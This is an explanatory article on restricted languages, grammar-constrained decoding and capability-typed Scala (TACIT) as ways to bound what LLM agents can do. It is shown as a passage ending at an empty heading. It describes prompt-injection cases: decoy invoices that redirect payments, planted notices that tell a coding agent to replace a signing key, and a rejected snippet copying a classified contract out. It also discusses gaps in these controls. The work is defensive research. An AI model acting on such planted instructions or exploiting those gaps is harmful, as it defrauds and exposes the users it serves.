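# Architectural constraints and restricted languages as a safety strategy for AI systems

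## What a restricted language is and what it promises

An architectural constraint on an AI system is a limit that engineers build into the software around a model, so that the model cannot take certain actions whatever it has learned in training. A restricted language is one such constraint. The system can act only by writing programs in a language with a deliberately narrow grammar, type system or set of operations, so that a program for certain kinds of harm either cannot be written in the language or fails a check before it runs. Computer scientists developed the idea before modern AI, as a way to run code from untrusted sources, and researchers have recently begun to treat AI models as untrusted sources too.

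An AI assistant in the accounts office of a small company might read invoices and contracts, summarise them for the staff, and pay the bills. It is built around a large language model, a program that takes in text and produces text. The model cannot pay anybody on its own, so the developers connect it to tools, which are functions that do things like open a file or send money. The surrounding software runs a tool whenever the model writes a request in the right format, known as a tool call. An agent is a model that acts through tools, usually over many steps, with the result of each call added to the text it reads next.

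Invoices are a risk because outsiders write them and can include text that the agent obeys as if it were an instruction from its user. This attack is called prompt injection. *NOMOS* (2026), which describes a way to turn written policies into checks on tool calls, gives an example. A user asks an agent to pay the bill in a file called bill-december-2023.txt. The file is a decoy containing a message in the user's name, which tells the assistant to begin by sending money to a certain account and to mention the user's music streaming service in the transfer. The agent tries to send a payment of 50 with the subject line "Spotify Premium". A check between the agent and the bank blocks it because the user never named that recipient and the account's history does not contain it. Prompt injection also happens outside the laboratory. Mascellino (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content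 Targets AI Agents*, reported that the security company Zscaler had found websites with hidden text meant to make agents send cryptocurrency payments.

Databases had a similar weakness, which programmers fixed at the level of the language. In an SQL injection, an attacker types a database command into, for instance, a web form, and the database runs it. A parameterised query prevents this by keeping the programmer's command separate from the user's text, so the database engine can never interpret that text as a command. Writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argued in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025) that language models cannot be fixed this way. A model only predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from the tokens before it, and nothing inside it separates instructions from data. David C therefore advised developers to assume that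 an attacker can steer the model, and to put deterministic safeguards on what the system can do.

Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) measured the problem in *AgentDojo*. They paired ordinary user tasks, including the December bill, with attacker goals, and planted the attacks in the emails, files and web pages that the agent reads. Fixed code then checks the simulated inbox or bank account and scores utility (whether the agent finished the user's task) and security (whether the attacker's goal was achieved) separately.

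### The claim

Write L for the language, p for a program in it, x for everything the program takes in while it runs (files, emails, replies from other services), and S for the set of behaviours that somebody has declared safe. Safety by construction is the claim that

**for every program p in L and every input x, behaviour(p, x) ∈ S.**

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), whose agents write programs in a typed language, defines behaviour as a trace, the sequence of tool calls in a run that have an observable side effect. For the accounts assistant, a short trace might be "save a summary, pay Acme 400", and S might contain every trace in which each payment goes to a supplier on the company's own list.

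Now suppose that L offers arithmetic, text handling and three operations on the world: reading a document, saving a summary, and calling pay(supplier, amount). The supplier must be an entry from the company's list, and no operation turns text into such an entry. A poisoned invoice may still lead the model to write a bad program, but that program cannot pay the attacker's account, because the account number in the invoice is text and pay does not accept text as a supplier. An entry on the list is a capability, an unforgeable value that gives a program holding it permission to use a resource.

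The guarantee covers every input, including attacks that nobody has thought of yet, whereas a test covers only the attacks that somebody tried. It also covers every program, including whatever a confused, hijacked or hostile author might write, so it does not depend on the author's intentions. In their proof, Zhou and colleagues model the language model as an oracle, an arbitrary function that returns some program, and assume nothing about which program it returns. If the program passes the type checker, it runs; if not, the call returns nothing. They then show that ordinary code in the host language could replace every call to the oracle without changing the traces, so any property the type system secures for ordinary programs also holds for programs with an agent inside.

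Some policies cannot be expressed as a set of allowed behaviours, because checking them requires comparing runs. Suppose the company wants the text of an invoice to have no influence on who gets the money. The trace "pay Acme 400" does not show whether the assistant followed that policy, since the money might have gone elsewhere if the invoice had read differently. For this reason, Schneider, Morrisett and Harper (2001), in *A Language-Based Approach to Security*, defined a security policy as a condition on the whole set of a program's executions. They showed that a monitor that watches a single execution and stops it just before a violation cannot enforce policies about the flow of information. A checker that reads the program's text has more information, because the text describes all possible executions. For policies of this kind, the claim becomes that for every p in L, the set of all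 behaviours of p, over all inputs, satisfies the policy.

A safety guarantee also holds for a language whose programs can do nothing. If a language has no payment operation, for example, none of its programs can make a bad payment. Schneider and colleagues note that enforcing a stricter policy also enforces a looser one, and that the strictest policy rules out every execution. A safety guarantee therefore doesn't show whether a language is useful, so evaluators have to measure safety and usefulness separately, as AgentDojo does.

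### Where the trust goes

The guarantee does not depend on trusting the model, but it does depend on a trusted base, meaning the parts that must be correct for it to hold, such as the compiler, interpreter, libraries, hardware and specification. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) have agents write in a restricted form of the programming language Scala. They trust the Scala compiler, their own library of permitted operations, the runtime that executes checked code and, where a user installs one, a local model that handles confidential text. They do not trust the cloud-hosted model that drives the agent, which they assume may be cooperating fully with an attacker, or any code it submits or document it reads.

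The value of this exchange depends on what goes into the base. Schneider and colleagues repeat an old principle of computer security, that an enforcement mechanism deserves the most confidence when it is small and simple. They contrast Windows 2000, which has millions of lines of source code, with a proof checker of about six pages of C, short enough for an engineer to read. A production compiler is far larger than the proof checker, and a bug in it could void the guarantee even if the model is not adversarial. Still, engineers know how to inspect, test and repair a compiler, while they have no comparable way to establish what a large neural network will do on every input.

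The choice of S needs just as much trust, because the claim covers only what S rules out. The rule in *NOMOS* about recipients seems sensible, and it stopped the streaming-service payment. But *NOMOS* also describes a variant in which the agent creates a transfer of zero dollars and puts the user's scheduled transactions in the subject line. A rule that only capped the amount would allow this transfer, which leaks information without moving money. Rules can also miss dishonest sellers. In *Agent Money Benchmark* (2026), a test of how agents spend money, repeat charges and prices above the list price made up 112 of 141 recorded scam events. A rule that permits any recipient the user has paid before can't stop a repeat charge, because the user has already paid that seller. To catch repeat charges, S has to refer to past receipts, and to catch inflated prices, it has to refer to the price list.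 The contract summaries are harder still. A rule can specify precisely which folder a summary should go to, but "the summary leaves out nothing important" has no obvious formal statement.

### Three places for a constraint

Engineers can constrain the form of a model's output. The accounts assistant might have to answer with a record that has fields for supplier, amount and due date, or to pick from a fixed menu. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes a customer-service agent that picks from a menu. It can fetch a link to the customer's last order, or refer the customer to the settings page for a password or payment details. The agent never sees the results of these actions, so an instruction planted in them cannot influence it. A constraint on form can guarantee that the amount field contains a number,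 but not that the number matches the invoice.

A constraint on effects limits what happens in the world. Examples are the pay operation with its list of suppliers and the check that blocked the streaming-service transfer. The model may write any calculation, as long as the resulting payments, emails and file changes stay inside S. Typed languages for agents are also constraints on effects, as is requiring a machine-checked proof before a program runs.

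Developers can also split the assistant into several parts and limit the messages between them. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider nearly the same job, in which an agent has to find this month's invoices among many files and email the information to the accounting department. In a naive design, instructions in one malicious file could make the agent read other files and mail them to the attacker. In the safer design, a separate model reads each file and reports only whether it contains an invoice, with a yes or no that cannot carry an instruction. Another model then sends the email about the files that got a yes. According to their analysis, a malicious file can then do no more than pass for an invoice, which its author could also have achieved by sending a real one. This holds only if the text of the files doesn't reach the model that sends the email by some other route.

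### The contrast with training

All of these constraints leave the model unchanged, whereas training changes it, for example by rewarding it for ignoring planted instructions. *APort Vault* (2026), a study of payment agents under attack, distinguishes cases where the model declines to request a transfer from cases where something between the model and the tool blocks it. According to the study, nearly all published measurement concerns the model's refusals.

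Those refusals have become much more reliable. In 2024, Debenedetti and colleagues' attacks succeeded against the best agents in just under a quarter of cases. When Zhou and colleagues tested four 2026 models on the part of AgentDojo that simulates a team's chat service, none of the 105 injected attacks succeeded, with no policy in force. In *Agent Money Benchmark*, the three best models (Claude Fable 5.2, GPT-6 Astra and Gemini 4 Argon) failed only one payment task out of 80. A company that uses one of these models might reasonably ask what a restricted language would add.

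In the same benchmark, GPT-6 Astra passed all 26 adversarial tasks, while GPT-6 Luna, from the same family, passed two. In nine further cases, a seller asked for a second payment for data that the agent already owned. Claude Opus 5.5 refused every time, and Claude Sonnet 5.5 paid every time. An office that moves its assistant to another model in the same family can lose the protection even if nothing else changes, whereas a check against past receipts would work the same way for both models. The scores also cover only attacks that somebody tried. Zhou and colleagues point to GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated system for attacking its own models, which consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues class training among the heuristic defences, which give some protection but no guarantee. They want it to be impossible for untrusted text to trigger a consequential action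 once an agent has taken it in.

Training has an advantage that no constraint can match, because a well-trained model may notice that a contract is odd in a way nobody thought to write into S.

### Origins

The word "capability" entered computing in 1966, when Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT designed a supervisor, the core of an operating system, for machines that ran many users' programs at once. *Early Capability Architectures*, a history of such systems, explains that each running program had a list of capabilities, and each entry named an object and what the program could do with it, such as read or write it. A program referred to an object by its position in the list, so it could not even name a file outside the list. A program could also start a subordinate program with an empty list and hand over only the entries it chose. MIT built the first working version on a small PDP-1 computer,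 and students used it until the mid-1970s.

Language-based security moved the enforcement of security policy from the operating system into programming languages. Schneider and colleagues motivated it with the Melissa and Love Bug viruses. An email carried a hidden script, which the mail program ran when the user opened the message. The script had all of the user's privileges, so it could read the address book and send itself on. The operating system did not step in because it treated the script's actions as the user's. Prompt injection repeats this pattern with English sentences in place of the script. The remedy was to analyse or rewrite programs before they ran, so that only those that could not violate the policy would run. The recipient only had to run the checker, while the producer had to write code that passed it, a task that falls to the model in the case of an AI agent.

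People who debate AI alignment, the problem of getting AI systems to pursue what their makers intend, argue more broadly that the way to get a secure and complex artefact is to restrict how it is built, rather than build it by arbitrary methods and try to secure it afterwards. For example, it is easy to write a program that certainly halts, but it can be impossible in practice to tell whether a program found on the internet will. In those debates the artefact is usually the AI model itself, billions of numbers produced by training, and the argument is a reason for pessimism about ever proving a model safe. Restricted languages apply the same rule to the programs the model writes, while the model itself remains unproven.

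### Objections

Attackers, or the model itself, may get around the constraint through a flaw in the trusted base or through a channel that S leaves out. People who approve a program or a specification may miss a small, well-placed error. A language rich enough for useful work may also be rich enough to express the harm.

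## Forcing a model's output into a grammar

A language model writes one token at a time. At each step it computes a probability for every token in its vocabulary, and the software that runs the model picks one using those probabilities. In constrained decoding, developers supply a grammar, a set of rules for which strings are well formed, and the software discards every token that would break the rules before picking. The accounts assistant could then write a payment record with a supplier, an amount and a due date, but it could not leave out a field or write a paragraph where the bank's software expects a number.

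### How the mask works

Software first turns the grammar into an automaton, a simple machine that reads text character by character and moves between states. Its current state records everything about the text so far that affects what the grammar allows next. Before each token is drawn, the software looks up which tokens the automaton can accept from that state. It sets the probability of all the others to zero, a step called masking, and scales up the rest so that they again sum to one. For example, suppose three tokens have probabilities 0.6, 0.3 and 0.1, and the grammar forbids the first. The other two sum to 0.4, and dividing each by 0.4 gives 0.75 and 0.25.

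In symbols, write P(t | w) for the model's probability of token t after the text w, and M(w) for the set of legal tokens, which *GrammarRL* (2026) defines as those that can still lead to a complete valid output. The masked probability of a legal token t is

**P(t | w) / Σ P(v | w), with the sum running over every v in M(w).**

*Efficient Guided Generation for Large Language Models* (Willard and Louf, 2023) gives the example of a grammar for decimal numbers and a vocabulary of five tokens: "A", ".", "42", ".2" and "1". At the start, only "A" is illegal. If the model writes ".2", the number already has its decimal point, so only "42" and "1" are legal next. Many earlier tools tested the whole vocabulary at every step. Willard and Louf instead ran each token through the grammar's automaton from every state in advance and stored the results in an index, so the legal tokens can be found with one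 lookup.

Numbers and dates have regular grammars, which a fixed number of states can handle. JSON, the usual format for tool calls, is harder because a record can contain a list of further records, and a fixed number of states can't track unlimited nesting. Such formats need a context-free grammar and a pushdown automaton, which adds a stack. Roughly, the automaton puts a marker on the stack when a bracket opens and removes it when the bracket closes. This slows the masking down, since one token may close several brackets at once, and whether that token is allowed then depends on markers deep in the stack. Vocabularies are also large, with about 128,000 tokens in Llama 3 and about 262,000 in Gemma 3.

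*Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (Li, Dong and colleagues, 2026) works out in advance which tokens each parser stack permits, so the software can read the stack once per step and look up a finished mask. It computed masks up to 700 times faster than earlier methods for programming languages and up to 30 times faster for JSON, and models generated text almost as fast as without a grammar. With agents, each request may come with different tools and therefore need a different grammar, so *XGrammar-2* (Li, Dong and colleagues, 2026, a separate team) reuses the parts that grammars have in common. Its engine prepared a grammar in about 10 milliseconds, while its predecessor needed more than 1,000, and function calls came within 6% of the unconstrained speed. Speed is therefore no longer much of an objection to constraining ordinary tool calls.

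According to *Decode-Time Grammars* (2026), the guarantee holds if the engine is exact and the output is complete. SynCode, for example, is not exact, because it saves time with an approximation that lets some invalid tokens through. Output can also be incomplete, because the mask does not force a model to stop. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (2025) describes models, more often small ones, that repeat themselves endlessly while obeying the grammar at every step. When such a run hits its length limit, the record is left incomplete and the surrounding software has to reject it.

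### From grammar to types

A grammatical program can still fail to compile because of a type error, such as passing a number to a function that expects text. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He et al., 2025) found that 94% of the compilation errors in TypeScript code written by six models were type errors and 6% were syntax errors. Context-free grammars can't in general express typing rules, because whether an expression is legal depends on earlier declarations in the program.

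Their automaton therefore records each variable's type as the program grows. In one example, the model has written "parseInt(num", where num is a number and parseInt requires text. A comma would be grammatical here, but it would leave parseInt with an argument of the wrong type. The software searches for chains of operations that lead from a number to text, finds ".toString()", and lets the model continue with it. A type checker for whole programs doesn't need this search because it sees only finished expressions.

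Type constraints cut compilation errors by more than half and raised the share of newly written programs that passed their tests by 3.5% in relative terms. Generation took 39% longer on one set of problems and 52% longer on another. The procedure favored the constraints, though, because Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without them and applied them only to new attempts at the failures. They did this because the automaton covers only part of TypeScript.

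Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, applied the constraint to every program, using the same six models, and the advantage disappeared. Unconstrained models wrote more working programs in almost every configuration. The best of them, Qwen2.5 32B, passed the tests 82.3% of the time without the constraint and 72.3% with it. Constrained models did worse because the constraint rejected some valid programs, such as those that call a function defined further down the file. When it blocked the most likely continuation, the model chose an unlikely one and often kept generating until it reached its time or token limit. When Biagiola and colleagues used a syntax constraint that accepted every valid program, constrained models did better than unconstrained ones, by 2.5% for a large model and up to 54% for a small one.

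A language restricted for safety deliberately leaves out many things that a model has learned to write, so it is likely to cause the same trouble. In Biagiola and colleagues' tests, fine-tuning (further training) on programs that satisfy the constraint reduced timeouts by 53% to 73%, and in some cases closed the gap with unconstrained generation.

### How masking distorts the choice

Suppose a payment record's supplier field may contain only "Acme Tools" or "none", and an invoice arrives from Acme Holdings, which is not on the company's list. The model gives the token "Acme" a probability of 0.9 and "none" 0.1. After "Acme", it would write "Holdings" 99% of the time and "Tools" 1%.

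Without the mask, the model would produce "Acme Tools" with probability 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009 and "none" with probability 0.1. If the company ran it repeatedly and kept only the valid answers, "Acme Tools" would make up 0.009 / 0.109 of them, or about 8%. With the mask, both first tokens stay legal because each can lead to a valid answer, so the software picks "Acme" 90% of the time. The mask then rules out "Holdings", which leaves "Tools" with all the probability. As a result, the assistant gives a well-formed answer that names the wrong company in nine cases out of ten.

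*Grammar-Aligned Decoding* (Park, Wang and colleagues, 2024) shows that correct sampling requires multiplying each token's probability by c, the chance that the model, continuing without the mask after that token, would produce a valid output. In the example, c is 0.01 for "Acme" and 1 for "none". Masking treats c as 1 whenever it is above zero. Park and colleagues asked a model for a string of zeros and ones ending in 1, which it produced about 90% of the time. They then imposed a grammar that allowed only 00000 and five-digit strings starting with 1. With masking, only 30% of the model's strings ended in 1, because whenever the first digit was 0, the model had to write 00000.

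Calculating c exactly would mean summing over all possible continuations, which is not feasible, so the proposed corrections estimate c or avoid calculating it. Rejection sampling, which discards invalid outputs and tries again, is exact but can take impractically long. Park and colleagues' method, ASAp, starts with masking and lowers its estimate of c each time a sample shows how much probability lay on invalid continuations. *Constrained Sampling for Language Models Should Be Easy* (2025) cuts a valid output at some point, has the model rewrite the rest under the mask, and repeats this in a way that gradually approaches the correct distribution.

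Repeated sampling takes a lot of compute. Özgü, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Parser Already Knows*, trained a small separate model to predict c from the state of the automaton and the candidate token. With this model's predictions, outputs were four to five times closer to the correct distribution than with plain masking, measured by a standard statistical distance, and generation took at most 1.25 times as long. ASAp took up to 20 times as long as masking and was, on average, further from the correct distribution. *GrammarRL* instead trains the language model itself while the mask is on, rewarding it for the quality of the whole output.

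Unlike that training, the corrections to sampling cannot fix the model's mistakes. A perfect correction restores the model's relative probabilities for the valid outputs, so if the model has mistaken Acme Holdings for Acme Tools, it will still pay Acme Tools. The grammar also has to include an answer like "none", or the model cannot decline to pay even a very suspicious invoice.

### Whether format limits harm reasoning

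*Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam, Wu and colleagues, 2024) reported that models reasoned markedly worse when they had to answer in a format such as JSON, and that the decline was generally larger with stricter formats. Either the mask or the request for a format could have caused the decline. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) separated the two effects by requesting a format with and without the mask. Across six open-weight models, the request alone lowered accuracy by an average of 3.9 percentage points, compared with 1.6 points for the mask.

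Three newer commercial models lost little or nothing when asked for a format. But one of them, GPT-5.4-nano, lost 59 points on mathematics problems when Lee and colleagues enforced XML with a mask. It filled the answer field with phrases about solving the problem and never did the calculation. It did fine with JSON, and they suspect that its training had covered only JSON. *Capacity, Not Format* (2026) also casts doubt on a general effect. It cites a causal analysis that found no influence of format in 43 of 48 scenarios, and concludes that format requirements hurt weak models most.

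In very small models the harm can be severe. In *The Constraint Tax*, Ray (2026) had a 1.5-billion-parameter model turn meeting requests into calendar entries. Every entry was valid whether the prompt merely described the format or a mask enforced it, but the share of correct entries fell from 91.5% with the prompt to 48% with the mask. Nearly all the errors were wrong durations. For example, the model gave a 30-minute meeting with Leo the right date, time, person and topic, but a length of 180 minutes.

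Models can avoid most of the loss by reasoning first and formatting the answer afterwards. Lee and colleagues let models answer freely and then reformat the answer in a second pass, which significantly improved accuracy in 42 of 72 comparisons and worsened it in two. Agents can do this within a single response, since engines such as XGrammar-2 don't constrain the text until the model writes the tag that opens a tool call. For a capable current model writing JSON, the harm to reasoning is therefore probably small. Small models running on a company's own machines, and formats that a model has rarely seen, need testing.

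### A valid payment to the wrong payee

Developers usually describe a tool call with a schema, which lists the fields of a record and the type of each. Anthropic's *structured outputs* documentation promises valid JSON, the right field types and no missing required fields. Suppose an invoice from Acme Tools is for 400, and the model writes a record that pays Birch Paper 4,000. The record still satisfies the schema, because it has a supplier, an amount and a date, all of the right type. The same is true whether the model misread the invoice or obeyed an instruction hidden in it.

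Errors of this sort are common. In *The Structured Output Benchmark*, Singh, Khurdula and colleagues (2026) had 21 models extract information into records. The models followed the schemas almost perfectly, but the best score for the values was 83.0% on ordinary text, 67.2% on text taken from scanned documents and 23.7% on meeting transcripts. The scoring was strict enough to count "United States" as wrong where the answer key had "American", but a valid record was still weak evidence of a correct one. *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026) tested tool calls. For Qwen3-8B, enforcing the schema raised the share of well-formed calls from 84.5% to 100%, but the share of correct calls rose only from 52% to 57.5%. Two other models already wrote well-formed calls every time, and enforcing the schema did not change their accuracy.

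A grammar can still rule out some harms. Like the pay operation described earlier, it can limit the supplier to the company's own list. It can also cap a payment, for example by allowing at most three digits before the decimal point. Not all commercial services support numeric limits. Google Cloud's *Structured outputs with Anthropic Claude models* notes that schemas there cannot limit the size of numbers, so a company using that service would have to enforce its ceiling elsewhere. The company also has to control the schema, because a schema written by an attacker can steer a model, as *When Grammar Guides the Attack* (2025) warns.

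In these cases, ordinary code could protect the bank just as well without masking, by reading each finished record and refusing any that named an unlisted supplier. Masking makes the system more useful because the model doesn't waste attempts on records that the code would refuse. A check on the finished record can also use information that the grammar lacks, such as last month's payments or the total on the invoice. Developers could put the correct total into the grammar too, but if the software already had the total, it wouldn't need a model to read the invoice.

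## Languages whose types limit what an agent can do

Checking one finished record at a time works for an agent that makes one tool call at a time. But many agents now write short programs that call several tools, loop over the results and do calculations between calls. Whether such a program is safe can depend on how its steps fit together. The accounts assistant may have good reason to read a confidential contract and to send a request to a web service, but a program that puts the contract in the request leaks it. A type checker checks the whole program before it runs, so it can reject that combination, as long as the types record what each piece of code can do.

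### Permission as a value

In most software, a program with permission to write files can write to any file it can name, so an attacker who controls the name can control how that permission is used. Security researchers call this the confused deputy problem, which *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) describes as a caller with little authority getting a program with more authority to misuse it on the caller's behalf.

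Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, give an example from programming. A developer asks an agent to repair some failing tests. An attacker has tampered with a test file so that it prints an official-looking instruction for the agent to replace the signing key in a source file with one the attacker controls. The source file has an ordinary name and belongs to the project the agent is supposed to edit, so a rule against touching sensitive files would not catch the change.

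The capabilities described earlier, called object capabilities in programming languages, avoid this by combining the name and the permission in a single value, such as an open file or a connection to one server. The holder of a capability can also derive a weaker one, such as access to one folder from access to a whole disk, and pass that on, but it can never derive a stronger one.

Bouras and colleagues borrowed part of this idea without changing the language. Their software, CapScope, keeps a table of permissions for each sub-agent, out of the model's reach, and checks every tool call a sub-agent makes against that sub-agent's table. In the example, the sub-agent that runs the tests also reads the fake notice, but it has no permission to edit source code. The attacker's action went through in 3 of 75 runs, compared with 33 to 47 of 75 when all the sub-agents had the same authority. The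 number of successful repairs hardly changed.

The model still refers to files by name, so Bouras and colleagues do not call CapScope an object-capability system. CapScope also checks each call separately, so a permitted read followed by a permitted write can still move a secret to the wrong place.

### Recording capabilities in types

Object capabilities alone do not solve that problem, because a function can hold a capability that its type does not show. Suppose the assistant passes a contract to a function that counts the words. The function's ordinary type, text in and number out, would be the same if it also held a network connection and sent the contract to somebody.

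Capture checking, an experimental extension of the Scala language, adds a capture set to each type. The set lists the capabilities that a value of that type may use. If f is an open file, a function that writes a piece of text to f has the type

**String ->{f} Unit**

where String is text and Unit means that the function returns nothing of interest. A function type with an empty set, such as String -> Int, is pure. A pure function can calculate and return a result, but it holds no capabilities, so it cannot write, print or send anything. The compiler works out most of the sets itself. It lets a function with a smaller set stand in where the program allows a larger one, and never the reverse. The sets are upper bounds, so the compiler may also reject a harmless function that holds f and would never have used it.

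Capture sets can also limit how long a permission lasts. In Odersky and colleagues' library, a program that requests a folder gets a capability valid only inside one block of code. An agent might try to keep its access by having the block return a function that reads the folder later. That function's type would have to mention the folder's capability, which has no meaning outside the block, so the compiler rejects the code. *Classifying Capabilities* (2026) extends the notation so that a type can limit or exclude whole kinds of capability at once.

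The theory behind this is fairly solid. *What's in the Box* (2025) gives a soundness proof for a formal model of the capture checker, and the proof-checking software Lean 4 has verified that proof. It also reports that Scala's collections library, about 30,000 lines long, needed only small and simple changes to work with the checker. *System Capybara* (2026) proves, also in Lean, that every well-typed program in a more powerful model produces only the traces that its capabilities authorise, which is safety by construction in the sense defined earlier. But both proofs cover small mathematical models of the language, not the real compiler that processes an agent's code. Scala's documentation still calls capture checking "highly experimental and unstable".

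### How TACIT checks a snippet

Odersky and colleagues built a system called TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) on top of capture checking. An agent connects to TACIT as it would to any other set of tools and sends it snippets of Scala. The compiler checks each snippet, which runs only if it passes. A snippet can reach files, the network or other programs only through a library of permitted operations. Some checks happen while the snippet runs, because it may compute a file's path from other data. If the path is outside the folder that the snippet asked for, the library refuses the request.

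Suppose the company has marked its contracts as classified. The library then returns their text inside a wrapper, Classified[String], which the agent cannot open. The agent can pass a function to the wrapper's map method, which applies it to the hidden text and wraps the result. Because map accepts only pure functions, the function cannot leak the text. If the agent prints the wrapper, it sees a row of asterisks, while the user sees the real text on a separate channel.

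The agent's own model runs in the cloud and never receives the text, so it cannot write a summary itself. It can send the wrapped text to a second model that the company trusts, and the answer comes back in a wrapper too. Adapted to the accounts assistant, a snippet that the compiler accepts looks like this:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/accounts") {
  val contract = readClassified("/accounts/contracts/acme.txt")
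  val summary = chat(contract.map(text => s"Summarise this: $text"))
  writeClassified("/accounts/contracts/acme-summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function passed to `map` only adds a few words before the text, so it is pure. The summary stays in its wrapper until it reaches another classified file.

Now suppose a poisoned invoice has persuaded the agent to copy the contract into an ordinary file, from which it could read the text back:

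```scala
requestFileSystem("/accounts") {
  val notes = access("/accounts/notes.txt")
  val contract = readClassified("/accounts/contracts/acme.txt")
  contract.map { text => notes.write(text) }
}
```

The compiler rejects this snippet because the function uses `notes`, which gives it the type `String ->{notes} Unit`, and `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The agent gets the error message and can try again. Agents wrote code like this in Odersky and colleagues' tests, including an attempt to print a GitHub key from inside `map`.

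A rejected snippet has no effects, because none of it has run. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up from the same laboratory, gives the example of an agent that has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as a number. The model's code does the subtraction but then returns a sentence, which is a type error. In a language that finds type errors only at run time, the balance would already have changed by then, and if the first line had made a payment, a retry could pay twice. In LACUNA the balance stays at 100, and the next attempt starts from there. A snippet that passes the type check can still fail halfway for reasons that no type checker can foresee, such as a bank's server going down.

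### Safe mode

Full Scala has several features that let a programmer override the type system. An agent could use them to make a capability disappear from a type, so TACIT restricts agents to a subset of the language known as safe mode. Scala's *Safe Mode* documentation gives six restrictions:

1. The code may not contain unchecked casts or pattern matches. A cast asserts that a value has a certain type without proving it, so it could pass off a function that writes to a file as a pure one.
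2. It may not use the module caps.unsafe, which contains ways around the tracking.
3. It may not use @unchecked annotations, which tell the compiler to skip a check.
4. It may not use runtime reflection, which lets a program inspect and call other code while running.
5. It must compile with capture checking switched on, and the compiler must also track changes to stored data.
6. It may use global objects only if their own code is safe, since a library call could otherwise have effects that no type records.

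Library writers sometimes need to break these rules. A cache, for example, stores earlier results in a variable that the compiler doesn't track, although callers get the same results either way. A programmer can mark such a module @assumeSafe, and the compiler accepts it without checking. The module then belongs to the trusted base, and a mistake in it could undo the guarantee for every snippet that calls it. The same annotation can also help users supervise agents. Scala's documentation sketches a mail function that asks the user to confirm each message and then passes it to a mailer that agents cannot call directly.

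Safe mode also does not restrict exceptions. Almost any line of code can fail, for instance by dividing by zero or running out of memory, and a function could reveal something about a secret by failing when it reads the secret. TACIT catches the failure at run time and turns it into an ordinary value, which the library can keep in its wrapper.

Odersky and colleagues describe the compiler as enforcing safe mode. But according to the project's code repository as of March 2026, lampepfl's *TACIT*, a separate validator enforced it by searching snippets for forbidden patterns. This check is weaker than a type system because it finds only the patterns that someone thought to list. Later documentation, copied on Glama's *TACIT* page, describes a switch for the compiler's own safe mode. One passage describes the switch as on by default and another as optional, so it is safer to set it explicitly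 when deploying TACIT.

### Tests of TACIT

To test security, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of secrets, such as passwords for online services. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted attacks, and added 11 requests in which the user asked for the secrets directly or posed as somebody entitled to them. Each model ran the resulting 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in the Classified wrapper and once with them in plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

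Both models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, were secure in every trial with the wrapper. Without it, Sonnet was secure in 98.5% of trials and MiniMax in 91.6%. Most of the leaks happened when the user was malicious. MiniMax leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 trials with malicious users, but in only 3 of the 120 with planted attacks. Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials with malicious users and in none with planted attacks.

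A working type system should produce a perfect score, so the experiment mainly tests the implementation. It also shows that the agents could still do ordinary tasks. With the wrapper, Sonnet completed 99.2% of them and MiniMax 90.0%, both higher than without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's lower figure in plain-text mode, 83.3%, is partly an artefact, because Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

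Odersky and colleagues used τ²-bench, in which agents serve simulated customers of an airline and a shop, to test whether having to write typed programs makes agents perform worse. All three models they tested did better with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points, which they credit to the clearly structured data and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, which contains 300 real software faults, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without, a difference of five faults. Compiling took less than a second, and at most 8% of the snippets on τ²-bench needed another attempt. Zhao and colleagues likewise found that agents using LACUNA roughly matched those using ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, solving 76.0% of 392 tasks.

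The result shows that models can write this kind of Scala with little or no loss in performance, but because none of the τ²-bench tools returned classified data, it doesn't show how much protecting such data lowers performance. Odersky and colleagues' version of AgentDojo, where emails, files and web pages arrive in wrappers, is a better test of that. Only one of 1,926 attacks counted as a success, and in that case the agent had booked the right hotel and merely quoted a review that mentioned the attacker's hotel. But the share of tasks completed ranged from 40% to 69%. With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks, against 81% for CaMeL, a system that fixes the agent's plan before the agent reads untrusted data.

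### What TACIT leaves out

Odersky and colleagues do not try to prevent wrong answers. An agent's summary of a contract may omit the most important clause, and type checking will not detect the omission. They also leave timing channels out of scope, so an agent could leak a secret one bit at a time by varying how long a pure function runs.

External commands are a more practical gap. Once a snippet starts another program, that program runs outside Scala, and the only guarantee left is what the list of permitted commands provides. Odersky and colleagues recommend listing only specific, safe commands and running the system in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits which files and network addresses a process can reach. Products such as Claude Code also come with their own file and command-line tools, which do not pass through TACIT, so lampepfl's instructions recommend switching those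 tools off.

The wrapper keeps classified data secret but does not protect it from tampering, because any agent can wrap its own text and write it over a classified file. Glama's copy of the documentation warns that an agent could replace the file that lists who may log in to a computer, and describes a setting that makes classified files read-only. The same version lets a snippet send classified data to web servers on an approved list, for example to log in to a service with a password that the agent can't see, so secrecy also depends on that list being correct.

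### Effect types and hidden constructors

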